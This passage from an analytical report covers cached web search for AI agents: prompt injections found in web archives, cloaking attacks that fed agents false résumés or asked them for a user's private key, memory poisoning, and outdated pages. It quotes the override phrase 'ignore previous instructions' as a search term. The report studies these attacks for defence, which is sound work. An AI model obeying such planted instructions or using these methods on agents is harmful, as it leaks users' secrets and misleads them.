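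An attacker may not need to know the schedule. Live requests in ordinary ChatGPT add pages to a shared cache, so someone could edit a public wiki and immediately ask ChatGPT to open the page. The cache could then keep the edit after volunteers had removed it from the wiki. This is an inference from RESONEO's results, and RESONEO did not test the attack. A provider could prevent it by letting only the crawler add pages to the cache.

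### What people plant in web pages

Khodayari and colleagues took most of their sample from Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. They searched about half of its October 2025 edition for 3,963 phrases typical of injections, such as "ignore previous instructions", and reviewed the matches. They confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages among 1.2 billion addresses, or about eight pages per million. Searches of Censys and Shodan, which catalogue machines connected to the internet, raised the total to 15,387.

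They sorted the injections by aim, and some had more than one:

| Aim | Injections | Typical request |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupting AI systems | 8,894 | Return random numbers |
| Protecting content or personal data | 4,093 | Do not train on this page |
| Identifying AI bots | 3,096 | Include a certain word if you are an AI |
| Unclear | 2,632 | Ignore previous instructions and do something else |
| Promoting a person, product or source | 1,521 | Give only a positive review |
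| Obtaining private data | 13 | Reveal secrets or the system's own instructions |

Fewer than one injection in a thousand attempted theft, the harm that cached browsing is meant to prevent. That proportion understates the value of caches, because one successful theft may matter more than thousands of requests for random numbers. A thief also has good reason to avoid a public archive, and can send the instructions by email instead. The search covered only known phrasings, so it missed injections in images, in most other languages and in unfamiliar wording.

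In *AI threats in the wild* (2026), Google's researchers scanned several monthly editions of Common Crawl and found that malicious injections rose 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. They don't say how many injections they found. They saw few attempts at data theft, all of them crude, and no significant use of the advanced methods that security researchers had published in 2025. They expect both the number and the quality of attacks to grow.

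Website operators had deliberately added about 81% of the injections in the Common Crawl sample, so an AI provider can't expect them to remove the text. Visitors' comments, like the one in the forum example, accounted for under 2%. Most injections also last a long time. Khodayari and colleagues checked older copies of the affected pages in the Internet Archive and found that 66% of the copies from a year earlier already contained an injection.

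### Scanning the store and withdrawing pages

A provider with a cache can scan each page before any agent reads it, whereas scanning live pages as they arrive makes the user wait. The bigger advantage is that the provider can search the stored pages again after learning about a new kind of attack, much as Google's researchers repeated their scan on successive editions of the archive.

Google used software to pick out pages with suspicious phrases, then used Gemini to check whether the text fitted the rest of the page, and had people review what remained. The later stages were necessary because most of the initial matches came from research papers, blog posts and articles about prompt injection. Khodayari and colleagues also found that more than half of the Common Crawl pages that matched their phrases were harmless. A provider that withdrew every match would remove a good deal of writing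 about AI security.

Two features of today's injections make them easier to find. Attackers and site owners reuse the same wording, so 54 templates covered 95% of the cases in the study. About 87% of the injections were also invisible to human readers. Many were in technical headers or comments in the page's code, and others were in tiny letters or the same colour as the background. Ordinary pages have some invisible text, but invisible text containing instructions for an AI is a strong warning sign.

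A provider can lose this clue by converting pages to plain text before scanning them. Khodayari and colleagues gave 13 models pages containing 100 different injections, in four formats, and asked for summaries. The models followed the injection in 3.9% of runs with plain text and 1.1% with the page's HTML. The HTML result is partly misleading, because long files exceeded some models' limits and caused errors in 20% of runs. But a shorter format that kept the page's structure also had a rate of 1.1%, with few errors. Small models did worst, following 8% of the injections in plain text. A provider should therefore scan the original code before simplifying the page.

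The study covered only summaries, so the rates could be higher or lower for agents with tools. A determined attacker can avoid familiar templates. OpenAI compares spotting a well-made injection to spotting a lie. The comparison also applies to stored text, although a provider has more time to examine it.

When a provider finds a page containing malicious instructions, it can withdraw the stored copy for every customer at once. It could also block the address for live fetches, but the attacker could then move the instructions to an approved address, or to a new one if the system allows any address. With a refusing cache, the attacker has to wait for the crawler to store another copy. The provider must also remove any copies derived from the page. RESONEO found that OpenAI keeps short extracts separately from full pages, so deleting only the full page might leave the instructions in search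 results.

Customers who share a cache generally read the same copy of a page, so if one reports strange behaviour by an agent, the provider can examine exactly what the agent read.

*A Whole New World* (Zychlinski, 2025) describes how an attacker can identify the model behind an agent from its answers to certain questions, then tailor an attack to that model's weaknesses. A stored page can't adapt to its reader. Stored copies also protect agents from a trap that Google's researchers found, in which a site sends AI visitors to a page that never finishes loading, though the crawler may still waste time on it.

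Providers say little about whether they scan stored pages for malicious instructions or withdraw the pages that contain them. OpenAI's help pages for Lockdown Mode and offline search mention neither practice. Google says it can process data on a global scale and neutralize threats before they reach users, but it doesn't say whether this covers the cache behind its URL context tool. The scan Google published was of Common Crawl, an archive it doesn't run.

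### Pages that only crawlers see

OpenAI tells people who use offline search to review the sources ChatGPT cites. But a user who opens a cited address gets the live page, which may differ from the copy ChatGPT read. The owner may have changed the page since, or the site may always have shown people one version and crawlers another. Websites have long used this second practice, called cloaking, to deceive search engines.

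The simplest way to recognise an agent is by the name in its request. OpenAI publishes the names of its crawlers so that site owners can recognise them, and an attacker can use the same list. A server can also check whether the request comes from a known data centre or whether the visitor moves the mouse as a person would. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) describes a system that records traces from the encrypted connection, the web request and the visitor's behaviour on the page. The researchers collected these traces from ChatGPT, Claude and Gemini agents, running each agent 30 times on the same seven pages.

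*OpenAI's new browser Atlas falls for AI-targeted Cloaking Attack* (2025) reports a test of cloaking in hiring by the security company SPLX, which invented a job and five candidates, each with a résumé on a web page. For one candidate, Natalie Carter, the server gave AI visitors a version with grander titles and more leadership experience. OpenAI's Atlas browser scored her 88 out of 100 and ranked her first. When the researchers supplied the résumés that people would see, the same model scored her 26 and ranked her last. The other four scores didn't change.

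The cloaked résumé contained false claims but no instructions, so a scanner looking for injections would have missed it. SPLX reports one ranking for each version and doesn't say how often it repeated the test. But a gap of 62 points, with the other scores unchanged, is unlikely to be due to chance.

Zychlinski used cloaking to obtain a secret. His test site showed people ordinary programming documentation, but showed AI agents a demand to authenticate themselves with a private key from the user's computer. The attack worked on the coding tool Cursor with each of the three models he tested: Claude 4 Sonnet, GPT-5 Fast and Gemini 2.5 Pro. He doesn't say how many times he tried it, and developers have since replaced these models with stronger ones.

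Both experiments used live visits, and a cache would change the result. In Zychlinski's design, the server gives known crawlers such as Google's the harmless page, so that they don't discover the attack. A cache filled by such a crawler would contain the harmless page, and agents reading from it would avoid the attack. To get past the cache, the attacker has to show the crawler the malicious page instead. The cache then holds a version that no human visitor sees, but the provider has a copy of the attack to examine.

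A provider can look for cloaking by revisiting a page with a program that resembles an ordinary browser and comparing the two versions. Zychlinski recommends disguising crawlers this way. The comparison would produce false alarms, because honest sites also change their advertisements and vary their pages by country or time of day. Disguising the crawler would also be awkward for a provider that has promised site owners a crawler they can identify and block.

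Researchers still know little about how often sites show malicious pages to AI agents and clean ones to other visitors. *Security of Deep Research Agents*, a survey published in November 2026, warns that people who check an agent's citations may see clean pages, and found no study devoted to the attack among its core papers. Common Crawl's archive can't settle the question, because a site that targets one company's agents could show Common Crawl's crawler a harmless page.

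### What an injection can do without sending data out

An attacker may not need an injection to make the agent give a false answer. Guerra and colleagues invented 56 topics on which the web had little or no information, and published one page of false claims about each. One page explained why small aircraft at the 2026 Singapore Airshow were all painted red. The researchers asked ChatGPT, Gemini and Perplexity's Sonar Pro about every topic in a neutral, an excited and a sceptical tone.

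In 31% of the 504 answers, the model used, cited or listed the planted page. Of the answers that used or cited it, 73% gave no warning. A sceptical question made a warning more likely but did little to keep the page out of the answer. The choice of website mattered far more. Pages on the established site often appeared in answers, while pages on new sites that the researchers hadn't submitted to Google never did.

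The test used live search on topics chosen for their obscurity, so the 31% doesn't apply to ordinary questions. An offline cache is less likely than live search to include an attacker's obscure page, but if it does, it may lack the pages that would contradict the attacker's.

OpenAI lists malware and security flaws among the risks of giving its coding agent, Codex, internet access. Cached search doesn't remove these risks, because a stored page may contain the bad advice. An injection could lead Codex to add a malicious package to a program even while Codex's own network access is off. If the developer later runs the program on a machine with an open connection, the package could send data out. OpenAI advises developers always to review Codex's work, which is sensible but depends on the developer spotting the problem.

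An agent that can run commands can also do damage locally. Google's researchers found web pages with commands that would delete all the files on the user's computer, though they thought these simple injections were unlikely to succeed. Deleting files needs no network connection, so if an agent followed such an injection, only limits on which files it can change, or a requirement that a person approve the command, would prevent the deletion.

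An injection may also alter the agent's memory, as Radware showed with ChatGPT. Zychlinski describes related research, *AgentPoison*, in which malicious examples in retrieved documents cause harmful actions long after the agent reads them. If the provider later withdraws the page, the altered memory remains. Someone investigating an injection therefore needs to check what the agent saved as well as what it read.

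A malicious instruction can also make the agent urge the user to click a link. Khodayari and colleagues found 1,262 copies of an instruction to send the user to a different website, all on a single site. The linked page might ask for a password, and the user may trust it because the assistant recommended it. ChatGPT's warning about unverified links may not appear, because a fake login page can have a public address that the crawler has already recorded. Opening a login page from a bookmark is safer than following a link in an agent's answer.

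## Outdated pages and the errors they cause

A stored page can lead an agent to a wrong answer even if nobody has tampered with it. Suppose a user asks when a pharmacy opens on Sundays. Four different faults could spoil the answer:

- The pharmacy changed its hours after the crawler stored the page, so the copy is outdated.
- The cache doesn't hold the page, and the agent answers from memory or from some other site.
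- The crawler received an error message or an empty layout instead of the hours, and the cache kept that.
- The copy has no capture date, so neither the agent nor the user can tell whether the hours are from last week or last year.

More frequent crawling helps with outdated copies, but it does nothing for a page that the crawler can't read.

### How often a stored copy is current

The standard formula comes from Cho and Garcia-Molina, in *Synchronizing a database to Improve Freshness*, who were working on Stanford's store of 42 million web pages. They assumed that a page changes at random, at an average rate of r times a day. The chance that a copy is still current t days after a refresh is then e^(−rt). Averaging this over the T days between refreshes gives the share of time that the copy is current:

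F = (1 − e^(−rT)) / (rT)

For a page that changes every ten days on average, r is 0.1. The right-hand column below uses their formula for refreshes at random times, 1 / (1 + rT), where T is the average number of days between refreshes.

| Time between refreshes | Current, with a regular schedule | Current, with refreshes at random times |
|---|---|---|
| One day | 95% | 91% |
| One week | 72% | 59% |
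| 30 days | 32% | 25% |

Cho and Garcia-Molina use the random case to describe a store that refreshes a page whenever a user happens to ask for it. Refreshing on demand therefore tends to leave copies older for the same number of visits, and it also risks leaking what the agent asked for.

To check whether pages change at random, they visited about 720,000 pages on 270 popular sites every day from February to June 1999. Among pages that changed every ten days on average, the gaps between changes closely matched the model. Daily visits could not show how often a page changed within a day, and four months was too short to learn much about pages that rarely change.

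The formula still holds if its assumptions do, but it needs current rates of change. *Risk-Constrained Freshness-Aware Semantic Caching for Open-Web Retrieval-Augmented LLMs* (2026) estimated some of these rates by fetching the top search results for thousands of questions, then fetching them again at intervals of up to a week. It gives each kind of question a half-life, the time in which half of the pages change. The last two columns apply the formula to these half-lives.

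| Kind of question | Half-life of the pages | Current, with daily refresh | Current, with weekly refresh |
|---|---|---|---|
| Timeless | 22 days | 98% | 90% |
| Slow-changing | 16 days | 98% | 86% |
| Medium | 15 hours | 60% | 13% |
| Fast-changing | 3 hours | 18% | 3% |

Pages go out of date at different rates, so an average for a whole cache is a poor guide to any one page. These figures also overstate the number of wrong answers, because the researchers counted a copy as outdated after any change to the page's main text, even a corrected typo. By this measure, even the pages for timeless questions had a half-life of only 22 days.

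The formula fails for pages that change on a fixed schedule. If a school posts a new lunch menu every Monday and the crawler visits every Tuesday, the copy is current six days out of seven. If the crawler visits every Sunday, the copy is current only one day out of seven. The formula gives 63% in both cases.

It also doesn't account for when people ask. People often visit a page just after it changes because they are interested in the change, and a stored copy is most likely to be wrong then.

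A provider that tries to maximise average freshness can make this worse. Cho and Garcia-Molina consider five pages that change once, twice, three, four and five times a day, and a crawler that can make five visits a day in total. Average freshness is highest when the crawler never visits the page that changes five times a day, because each new copy would soon be out of date. The page that changes twice a day gets the most visits, about 1.4 a day.

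For a store of 100 million pages, refreshed once a month on average, they estimated that the best plan would keep 62% of copies current. Visiting every page equally often would keep 57% current, and visiting pages in proportion to how often they change would keep only 12% current. These estimates treat every page as equally important, though a list of security updates and a celebrity news page, for example, differ in importance. Their preliminary result was that more important pages should be visited more often, though not necessarily in proportion to their importance.

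### Why a missing date is worse than an old one

A capture date helps a reader decide how far to trust a copy. If a page changes every ten days on average and its copy is refreshed every 30 days, a copy from yesterday has about a 90% chance of being current, and one from four weeks ago has about a 6% chance. Without a date, the reader can only assume the average over the 30 days, 32%, for both.

Many pages also contain words that make sense only with a date. OpenAI's own help page for offline search included the line "Updated: 17 days ago". That line never changes in a stored copy, so nobody can work out when the page was updated without knowing when the crawler visited. The same is true of "latest version" and "this Friday".

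OpenAI does not guarantee when any address will be refreshed, or that offline results will include a capture time. It tells customers not to use offline search for audit-grade evidence of what a page contained at a certain moment, or for proof that a source was current when ChatGPT answered. It recommends the feature for stable research rather than the latest information. That is good advice, but users have to recognise which questions need current information, and they may not realise that "which version should I install?" is one of them.

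In *Codex Web Search vs Firecrawl*, Hiba Fathima describes asking Codex for a library's latest changelog and getting confident, detailed instructions that were entirely wrong. The library had made a major breaking change three weeks earlier. Fathima says Codex had searched its default cache and gave no date or warning. Firecrawl sells a competing search tool and the post doesn't name the library, so this is weak evidence about how often such errors happen. But it shows how hard they are to notice, since nothing in the answer looked old.

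Live search shortens the delay but doesn't always remove it. In *Fetch, Read, Reuse*, Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026) put unguessable codes in pages on their own websites and asked search services about those pages from September to November. After a page changed, answers from OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI could reflect the old version for about 30 minutes to a day or more, without showing the copy's age. All three services shared fetched pages between accounts, though Anthropic's documentation doesn't specify whether its service does. They also largely ignored Cache-Control, the header a website uses to specify how long others may reuse a copy.

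### What models do with outdated text

Experiments suggest that models often fail to recognise and disregard old information. In *HoH*, Ouyang, Pan and colleagues (2025) compared monthly copies of Wikipedia to find facts that had changed, and wrote 96,124 questions about them. They gave models a passage with the current answer, with or without a second passage containing the old one. Each prompt included today's date, the date of every passage, and an instruction to prefer the most current information.

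The scores below are the percentage of right answers minus the percentage of wrong ones, and answers of "I don't know" count as zero. Every prompt also included two irrelevant passages.

| Model | Current passage only | Current and outdated passages |
|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 70B | 88.7 | 66.2 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 84.5 | 49.1 |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 73.1 | 33.8 |

The largest model did best, but its rate of wrong answers still rose from 4% to 15%. No passage order worked well for every model, since putting the newest passage first helped the largest but badly hurt the smallest.

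A cache normally keeps one copy of a page, so the agent may see only the old version. In the experiment, outdated passages were riskier for the models than missing ones. Models given only outdated passages often answered confidently and wrongly. When the search found neither the current nor the old passage, they were more likely to admit that they didn't know.

The HoH models date from 2024, but newer models have the same weakness. *Stale-Document Poisoning* (Ahmed, Galke Poech and Röttger, 2026) collects 317 cases in which official guidance reversed. For example, doctors once routinely gave beta-blockers after a heart attack even if the heart still pumped normally, but later guidance withdrew or narrowed that advice. The researchers first found questions that a model answered correctly without documents, then gave it one genuine but outdated document and asked again.

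GPT-5.5 abandoned its correct answer in 74 of 83 medical cases. In tests of open models, Llama gave up 30% of its correct answers and Qwen 37% when the prompt did not tell them to trust the document. When the prompt told them to follow it, the rates rose to 66% and 75%. The rates were lowest on software questions, at 17% to 35% even with that instruction.

The open models also followed up-to-date documents in 97% to 100% of trials, as they should. A provider can't fix the problem by training models to distrust whatever they retrieve, because most of the value of search comes from models accepting corrections to what they remember.

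Ahmed and colleagues then tested whether dates would help. For each of 50 reversals, they showed models the same old document twice, once saying that the current date was before the reversal and once saying that it was after. Changing the date changed the answers only slightly. But when the prompt also stated when the old guidance had stopped applying, Qwen 2.5 72B switched to the right answer in all 50 cases, and Llama 3.1 70B in at least 47.

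A page captured before its advice was reversed can't include the date the advice expired. That date has to come from a newer page, which the cache may not have. A model therefore needs some evidence that something has changed, as well as capture dates.

Neither experiment measures how often a deployed cache causes errors, because the researchers made sure that outdated text reached the model. That rate also depends on how often a search returns an outdated page and on what else it returns. An agent that reads five websites may find the current answer on four of them. Ouyang and colleagues note that their old passages were earlier versions of the same articles, and so more alike than outdated pages on the real web.

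A store that keeps several versions of the same information can also return an outdated one, because the old version matches a question about as well as the new one. *StaleBench* (2026) tested this in agents' memories and found that similarity search returned the outdated version of a fact 53% of the time. A web cache that replaces its old copies mostly avoids this problem. However, OpenAI stores short extracts separately from full pages, so an agent could find one version of a page in its search results and read another when it opens the page.

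### Agents on frozen and live pages

Researchers often test agents on frozen collections of pages so that every agent has the same material. *DeepResearchGym* (2025), for example, lets agents search two large public collections instead of the live web. Some tests require old pages. FutureSearch, a research company, has agents forecast the answers to 2,386 questions that have since been settled, and agents with access to the live web could look up what happened.

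The company also compared stored pages with the live web in *Deep Research Bench* (Bosse, Evans and colleagues, 2025). Each agent did 89 research tasks, such as finding the total number of medical device recalls in a certain class. It did them both on the live web and with RetroSearch, a system that supplies only pages the researchers had already collected.

Nine of the 11 models scored lower on the frozen pages. On a scale from 0 to 1, o3's score fell from 0.51 to 0.46, and Claude 3.7 Sonnet's, without extended thinking, fell from 0.48 to 0.39. Gemini 2.5 Pro's rose from 0.45 to 0.46. The average for all 11 fell from 0.39 to 0.35. There were only 89 tasks, with two attempts at each, so some of these differences are probably noise, but the general direction is plausible.

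Missing pages probably explain more of the drop than outdated ones. The researchers ran all the tests within two months, so most of the pages had little time to change. RetroSearch also removes any search result whose page it doesn't have, which leaves the agent with fewer sources.

Bosse and colleagues searched for material relevant to each task and typically stored between 10,000 and 111,000 pages per task, depending on its type. A deployed cache could easily do worse, because its provider doesn't know users' questions in advance. However, Bosse and colleagues point out that a frozen collection can also make a task easier by leaving out misleading pages that an agent would meet on the live web.

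RetroSearch would not be a suitable defence against leaks. It first sends every query to a live Google search, then keeps only the results for which it has stored pages. The live search makes the test more realistic, but in a product it would send the agent's queries to outside companies.

In *BrowseComp-Plus*, Chen, Ma and colleagues (2025) show how much an agent's accuracy depends on its search tool, even when the stored pages stay the same. They built a fixed collection of 100,195 documents for 830 difficult questions. GPT-5 answered 55.9% correctly with a traditional keyword search and 70.1% with a search system based on a language model. Claude Opus 4 rose from 15.5% to 36.1% with the same switch. An agent may therefore fail to find a page that is in the cache, and the user would see the same result as if the page were missing.

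Those scores come from a collection that human reviewers had checked for the necessary evidence. The researchers also dropped 137 of 1,142 candidate questions because their software couldn't retrieve every page listed as evidence. Some retrievals failed because a model had invented the addresses. A commercial cache can't drop users' questions when the pages they need are hard to capture. *BrowseComp-Plus* has no live-web comparison, so it can't show how much accuracy an agent loses by going offline.

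### Pages the crawler captured badly

When a web server sends a page successfully, it labels the response with the code 200. Software often treats this code as a sign that it received the page, but the response may contain only a request that the visitor prove they are human.

In *When 200 OK Is Not an Answer*, Zhang (2026) used a simple program to request 7,293 pages over three days in October without running their scripts. About 60% came back with code 200, which signals success, but 20.9% of those lacked the page's main content. Some were blocking notices, bot checks, error messages or a homepage instead of the article. On popular sites, the most common failure was a page with menus and a footer but little or none of the main text, which appears only after a browser runs the page's scripts.

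The true figure may be somewhat lower. A language model labelled the pages, and a closer review of a sample put the share at 20.0%, compared with 25.5% from the model's labels. The study also measured live fetches, not cached pages. All the requests came from one location and appeared to come from an ordinary Chrome browser. A well-known crawler might get through more often, or less often if a publisher blocks it.

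Storing a faulty response makes the fault last longer. An agent that runs into a temporary bot check during a live fetch can try again a minute later, but if a crawler that visits every 30 days stores the bot check page, agents may get that useless copy for a month. Refreshing a page can also make the cache worse, by replacing a good copy with a useless one.

Zhang's test of cited sources shows how easily software can mistake an unusable response for the cited page. The test compared passages from web pages in 2023 with the same pages in 2026 to see whether the pages still supported the claims that cited them. When the software treated every HTTP 200 response as the page, 21.9% of the sources seemed to no longer support their claims. When it excluded unusable responses, the figure fell to 5.8%.

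Services can lose content in other ways too. Chen, Canini and colleagues found that OpenAI's search tool discarded some file formats after fetching them, and that xAI's read only the first half-megabyte of a page without notifying the user. No service they tested read text that appears only after JavaScript runs. The services also cached failed fetches, so a page could stay missing from answers even after its owner fixed the problem.

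Simple checks catch most bad captures. Zhang's best combination of checks flagged a response if it had fewer than 930 characters of text, redirected a specific address to the site's homepage, or resembled what the site returned for a made-up address. This found 86% of the unusable responses in the reviewed sample and wrongly flagged about 6% of the good ones. A cache can also compare the new response with the old copy, which a live tool doesn't have. If an article of 2,000 words now has 40, the provider should keep the old copy, with its original date, until a later visit succeeds.

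Opening flagged pages in a full browser recovers many of them. In Zhang's test this took about 12 times as long as a simple request, typically 20 seconds instead of under two. A user waiting for an answer would notice the delay, but not if a crawler had already fetched the page.

### A hypothetical question about PHP

On 21 October 2026, the developers of PHP released emergency fixes for two critical flaws, as The Next Web reported that month in *PHP rushes out emergency patches*. PHP is a programming language that runs a large share of the world's websites. The following example is hypothetical, but it shows how an accurate copy of an official page can produce dangerous advice:

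1. On 20 October, a provider's crawler stores PHP's download page, which lists the latest version. Call it version A.
2. On 21 October, the developers release version B, which fixes the flaws, and update the page.
3. That evening, someone setting up a web server asks an agent which PHP version to install.
4. The agent reads the copy from the day before and recommends version A, citing the official page.

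The new server has two critical flaws that the developers have already fixed. This happened even though nobody attacked the agent and the cache worked as designed.

A copy can be current most of the time and still carry this risk. Suppose the download page changes every 30 days on average and the crawler refreshes its copy every week. According to the formula, the copy is current 89% of the time. But if someone asks one day after a release, there is only a one-in-seven chance that the crawler has revisited the page since the release. Daily refreshes raise the average to 98%, but a question asked on the evening of a release can still get the wrong answer.

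A visible capture date might not help much either, because a copy from the day before looks fresh. The relatively good results for software in the study by Ahmed and colleagues are not very reassuring here, because those models already knew the right answer before they saw the old document. A model in use on the day version B is released could not have learned about it in training.

The agent might find both the old download page and a news story about the fixes. Ouyang and colleagues tested this kind of conflict, and a good model would probably recommend version B, though not every time. The user can also catch the error by opening the live version of the cited page.

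The error is harder to catch with a coding agent. If the agent writes version A into a project's configuration file, the project may keep installing that version even after the cache has a new copy of the download page. The user may also never read the sentence in which the agent chose version A.

### Ways to reduce the errors

Providers could start by giving every stored page a capture date and showing it to the model and the user. This is feasible, since OpenAI's and Anthropic's developer tools already report some dates. The date has to be right because the collection date given to a document can change a model's answer, as the title of *Collection-Date Assignment Redirects Answers in Temporal QA* (2026) indicates.

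Since models respond weakly to dates, ordinary software should help handle outdated pages. It could warn the user when a copy is older than a limit for that kind of page, perhaps a year for an encyclopedia article and an hour for a security notice. Software can also rank newer pages higher, but this can push current pages out of the top results along with outdated ones. In the HoH experiments, it reduced the share of searches with an outdated document in the top five results from 88% to 50%, and the share with a current one from 87% to 70%. Ahmed and colleagues tested a more selective method that also looked for signs that newer guidance had replaced a document. It reduced the errors from outdated documents by 5 to 10 percentage points when the dates were accurate.

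For pages where a day's delay matters, an organisation could let its agents fetch a short list of approved addresses live, such as the official release pages for the software it uses. This would give the right answer in the PHP example. The agent's choice among those pages still sends a little information to their owners, so the list should contain only exact addresses on sites that outsiders don't control.

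A provider can avoid even that by refreshing the pages on the list on a fixed schedule. Visiting 500 release pages every hour would take 12,000 requests a day, fewer than OpenAI's crawler made to a single test site in an hour. An agent would then be at most about an hour behind a new release.

Users can also supply the document themselves when a stored page is outdated, missing or badly captured. OpenAI recommends using an official document or archived record to establish what a page contained on a certain date. Supplying a document depends on the user suspecting a problem, though. Someone who needs the current PHP release should type the official address into a browser and give the agent the text from that page.

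## Who controls the cache

Serving an agent stored copies shifts control over what it reads from each website's owner to the cache provider, which chooses which pages to store, when to capture them and how long to keep them. Outside websites learn less about what the user reads, but the provider serves every page and can record every request. Users therefore trust fewer organizations, but they have to trust the provider more.

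### Five decisions about stored pages

The keeper of a cache decides which pages to include, which version of each to keep, when to refresh it, what to remove, and who may inspect the collection. For OpenAI's offline web search, the documented powers are as follows:

| Decision | OpenAI | Customer | Publisher | Person named on a page |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Which pages enter | Crawls and selects them | Can't add any, but can paste or upload a page for one chat | Can admit or refuse the crawler | Can ask the publisher to refuse it |
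| Which version stays | Decides | Can't choose | Controls what the crawler receives | Can ask the publisher for a correction |
| When to refresh | Decides, with no promise for any address | No documented way to request it | No documented way to request it | No documented way to request it |
| What to remove | Can delete any copy | Can disregard a source | Can opt out of search | Can make a legal request in some countries |
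| Who may inspect | Holds the whole collection | Sees the sources ChatGPT cites | Sees the crawler's visits, but not later readings | Can request their own data in some countries |

Customers also can't tell why a page is missing. OpenAI lists several possible reasons, including that the publisher blocks crawlers, that the page needs a login, and that OpenAI judges the page "low-signal", a term it doesn't define. A provider that left out criticism of itself would be hard to catch, because the missing pages would look like pages the crawler had never found.

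In Codex's indexed mode, OpenAI decides which live addresses an agent may open. According to Daniel Vaughan, it does this on its server, using its own content policies and index. If a company relies on a supplier's manual that OpenAI hasn't approved, the company can't add the address. Its developers have to supply the text themselves or switch to live search, perhaps limited to the supplier's domain.

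This inflexibility also makes the check harder to defeat. If the list of approved addresses were in a project's settings, planted instructions could lead Codex to edit it.

### What the provider can record

A provider that fetches live pages for an agent already sees every address, because the requests pass through its servers. Switching to a cache hides the user's reading from websites without showing the provider anything new. But if the user used to read those pages in a browser, the provider can now see which pages they request. For a law firm, a list of requests for pages about one small company could reveal a planned takeover.

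According to OpenAI's documentation, the company by default keeps abuse-monitoring logs of API use for up to 30 days. These logs may contain prompts and responses, and OpenAI can keep them longer if the law requires it or to prevent harm. Its main interface for developers also stores responses for at least 30 days unless the developer turns storage off.

Some customers can get stricter terms. In *Offering Zero Data Retention for frontier models*, OpenAI promises eligible API customers that it won't keep their prompts or responses after processing a request. Customers need OpenAI's approval, and OpenAI still keeps images that its software flags as possible child abuse material. It can also exclude particular models from a customer's arrangement after giving written notice.

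OpenAI's agreement for handling US patient data excludes live web search. It can cover cached search, but only in a project with Zero Data Retention. Evidently, OpenAI doesn't consider caching enough to protect medical records if it also logs what people ask.

These terms cover the API and may not apply to ChatGPT. OpenAI's help page on offline search gives no retention period and doesn't mention logs. An administrator should ask whether OpenAI records the addresses that ChatGPT opens from the cache, how long it keeps them, and which staff can read them.

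A court can also override a retention policy. In 2025, the US court hearing The New York Times's copyright case against OpenAI ordered the company to preserve ChatGPT and API output that it would otherwise have deleted. The obligation to keep new output lasted from May to September. The order didn't affect API customers with Zero Data Retention, because OpenAI didn't store their output.

Customers need records of their own to investigate an incident:

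- OpenAI can give developers every address the model consulted, which is often more than it cites. The response usually includes the search queries too, and shows when the model opened a page.
- AWS can log who used Bedrock's search tool and when. For each successful fetch, the log shows whether the tool could use only the cache or could fall back to the live web, so an auditor can check that an offline policy worked. The logging is off by default and costs extra.
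- Anthropic's developer tool returns the text it retrieved along with the retrieval time, as Chen and colleagues found. A developer who saves both can later show what the agent read.

An address alone can't establish this, because the provider may have replaced the stored copy since.

### What publishers can refuse

Publishers have traditionally controlled crawlers with robots.txt, which can set separate rules for each crawler by name. OpenAI uses three names that matter here:

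| Name | Purpose | Effect of a robots.txt block |
|---|---|---|
| GPTBot | Collecting training data | Tells OpenAI not to train on the site |
| OAI-SearchBot | Search | Removes the site from ChatGPT's search answers, though links to it may remain |
| ChatGPT-User | Visits that a user's request triggers | Possibly none |

A change to the search rule takes effect after about 24 hours. For visits that users trigger, OpenAI says robots.txt "rules may not apply". PPC Land reported that OpenAI adopted this position on 9 December 2025, when it removed wording that listed ChatGPT-User among the crawlers that follow robots.txt.

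OpenAI's reason is that a person starts the visit. This would make sense if ChatGPT fetched the page once for that person, as a browser does, but OpenAI also keeps the page and uses it to answer other customers. RESONEO found that user-triggered visits add pages to ChatGPT's cache, so a page could enter the cache even if its publisher had blocked the search crawler. OpenAI doesn't say whether it deletes such copies.

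Other companies behave differently. In tests by Chen and colleagues, Anthropic's software checked robots.txt before 99.9% of its page requests. xAI's requests looked like those of an ordinary browser and came from more than a thousand networks, so a publisher would struggle to recognise them. Until 15 October 2026, Anthropic reused stored copies of pages marked "no-store", an instruction not to keep a copy. From 17 October, it fetched the researchers' marked pages afresh for every question. This change benefited publishers, but it depended on Anthropic choosing to follow the instruction.

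A block by a content-delivery network is harder to ignore, because the network delivers pages on a website's behalf and can refuse a crawler's request before it reaches the site. Cloudflare, one such network, has asked the owners of new domains since July 2025 whether to block AI crawlers. *Detecting Bot Detection* (2026) describes networks that block AI crawlers by default and others that let websites charge for each crawl.

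Payment per crawl fits poorly with a shared cache. If a publisher charges one cent per visit and the cached copy serves 10,000 answers, the publisher earns one cent instead of $100. Chen and colleagues point out that the publisher can't count those answers, because reads from the cache never reach its server. A fair price would depend on use, which only the provider can measure.

Small sites have little bargaining power. *terms.txt* (2026), a proposal for a system of consent and payment, argues that robots.txt only states a preference and can't serve as a licence. It also cites Cloudflare, which says small sites must choose between allowing AI training and becoming harder to find.

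### How blocking changes the sources an agent sees

Estimates of how many sites block AI crawlers vary widely, partly because they measure different things. The table below uses *Web Crawler Restrictions, AI Training Datasets & Political Biases* (2025), specification.website's *robots.txt for AI crawlers*, Lawenda's *Who sets the consent signal?* (2026), and Zhang's test of page requests.

| Date | Sample | What the sites did | Share | Source |
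|---|---|---|---|---|
| August–September 2025 | Top million websites | Blocked GPTBot completely | 10.6% | *Web Crawler Restrictions* |
| August–September 2025 | Top million websites | Blocked ChatGPT-User completely | 6.5% | *Web Crawler Restrictions* |
| September 2026 | 668,523 websites | Had any rule for AI crawlers, including permission | 13.1% | specification.website |
| October 2026 | 3.4 million websites under five countries' domains | Opted out of AI training | 0.7% (Germany) to 3.8% (Czech Republic) | Lawenda |
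| October 2026 | 7,293 pages | Refused a simple automated request | 21.5% | Zhang |

Popular sites opt out more often. In Lawenda's data, sites on a popularity list were 3.6 to 13 times as likely to opt out as others under the same country's domain. Among the 131 German sites in the world's top 10,000, 31.3% opted out. Agents tend to need pages from popular sites, so the low national averages understate the problem.

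Opt-out counts overstate how many sites are closed to search caches, because a site that refuses only training can still appear in one. In the Czech data, 93% of opt-outs were limited to training. Most of these came from one company, Shoptet, which runs online shops and made the opt-out its default setting in August or September 2026. If Shoptet had refused search crawlers instead, thousands of shops could have disappeared from caches without their owners choosing this.

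News is a more worrying case. Lawenda cites *Is Misinformation More Open?* (2025), which found that 60.0% of reputable news sites with a robots.txt file refused at least one AI crawler, compared with 9.1% of misinformation sites. If 90 reputable sites and 10 misinformation sites covered a story, and a cache lost every site that refused any AI crawler, it would keep 36 reputable sites and about nine misinformation sites. The share of sources that were misinformation sites would rise from 10% to 20%.

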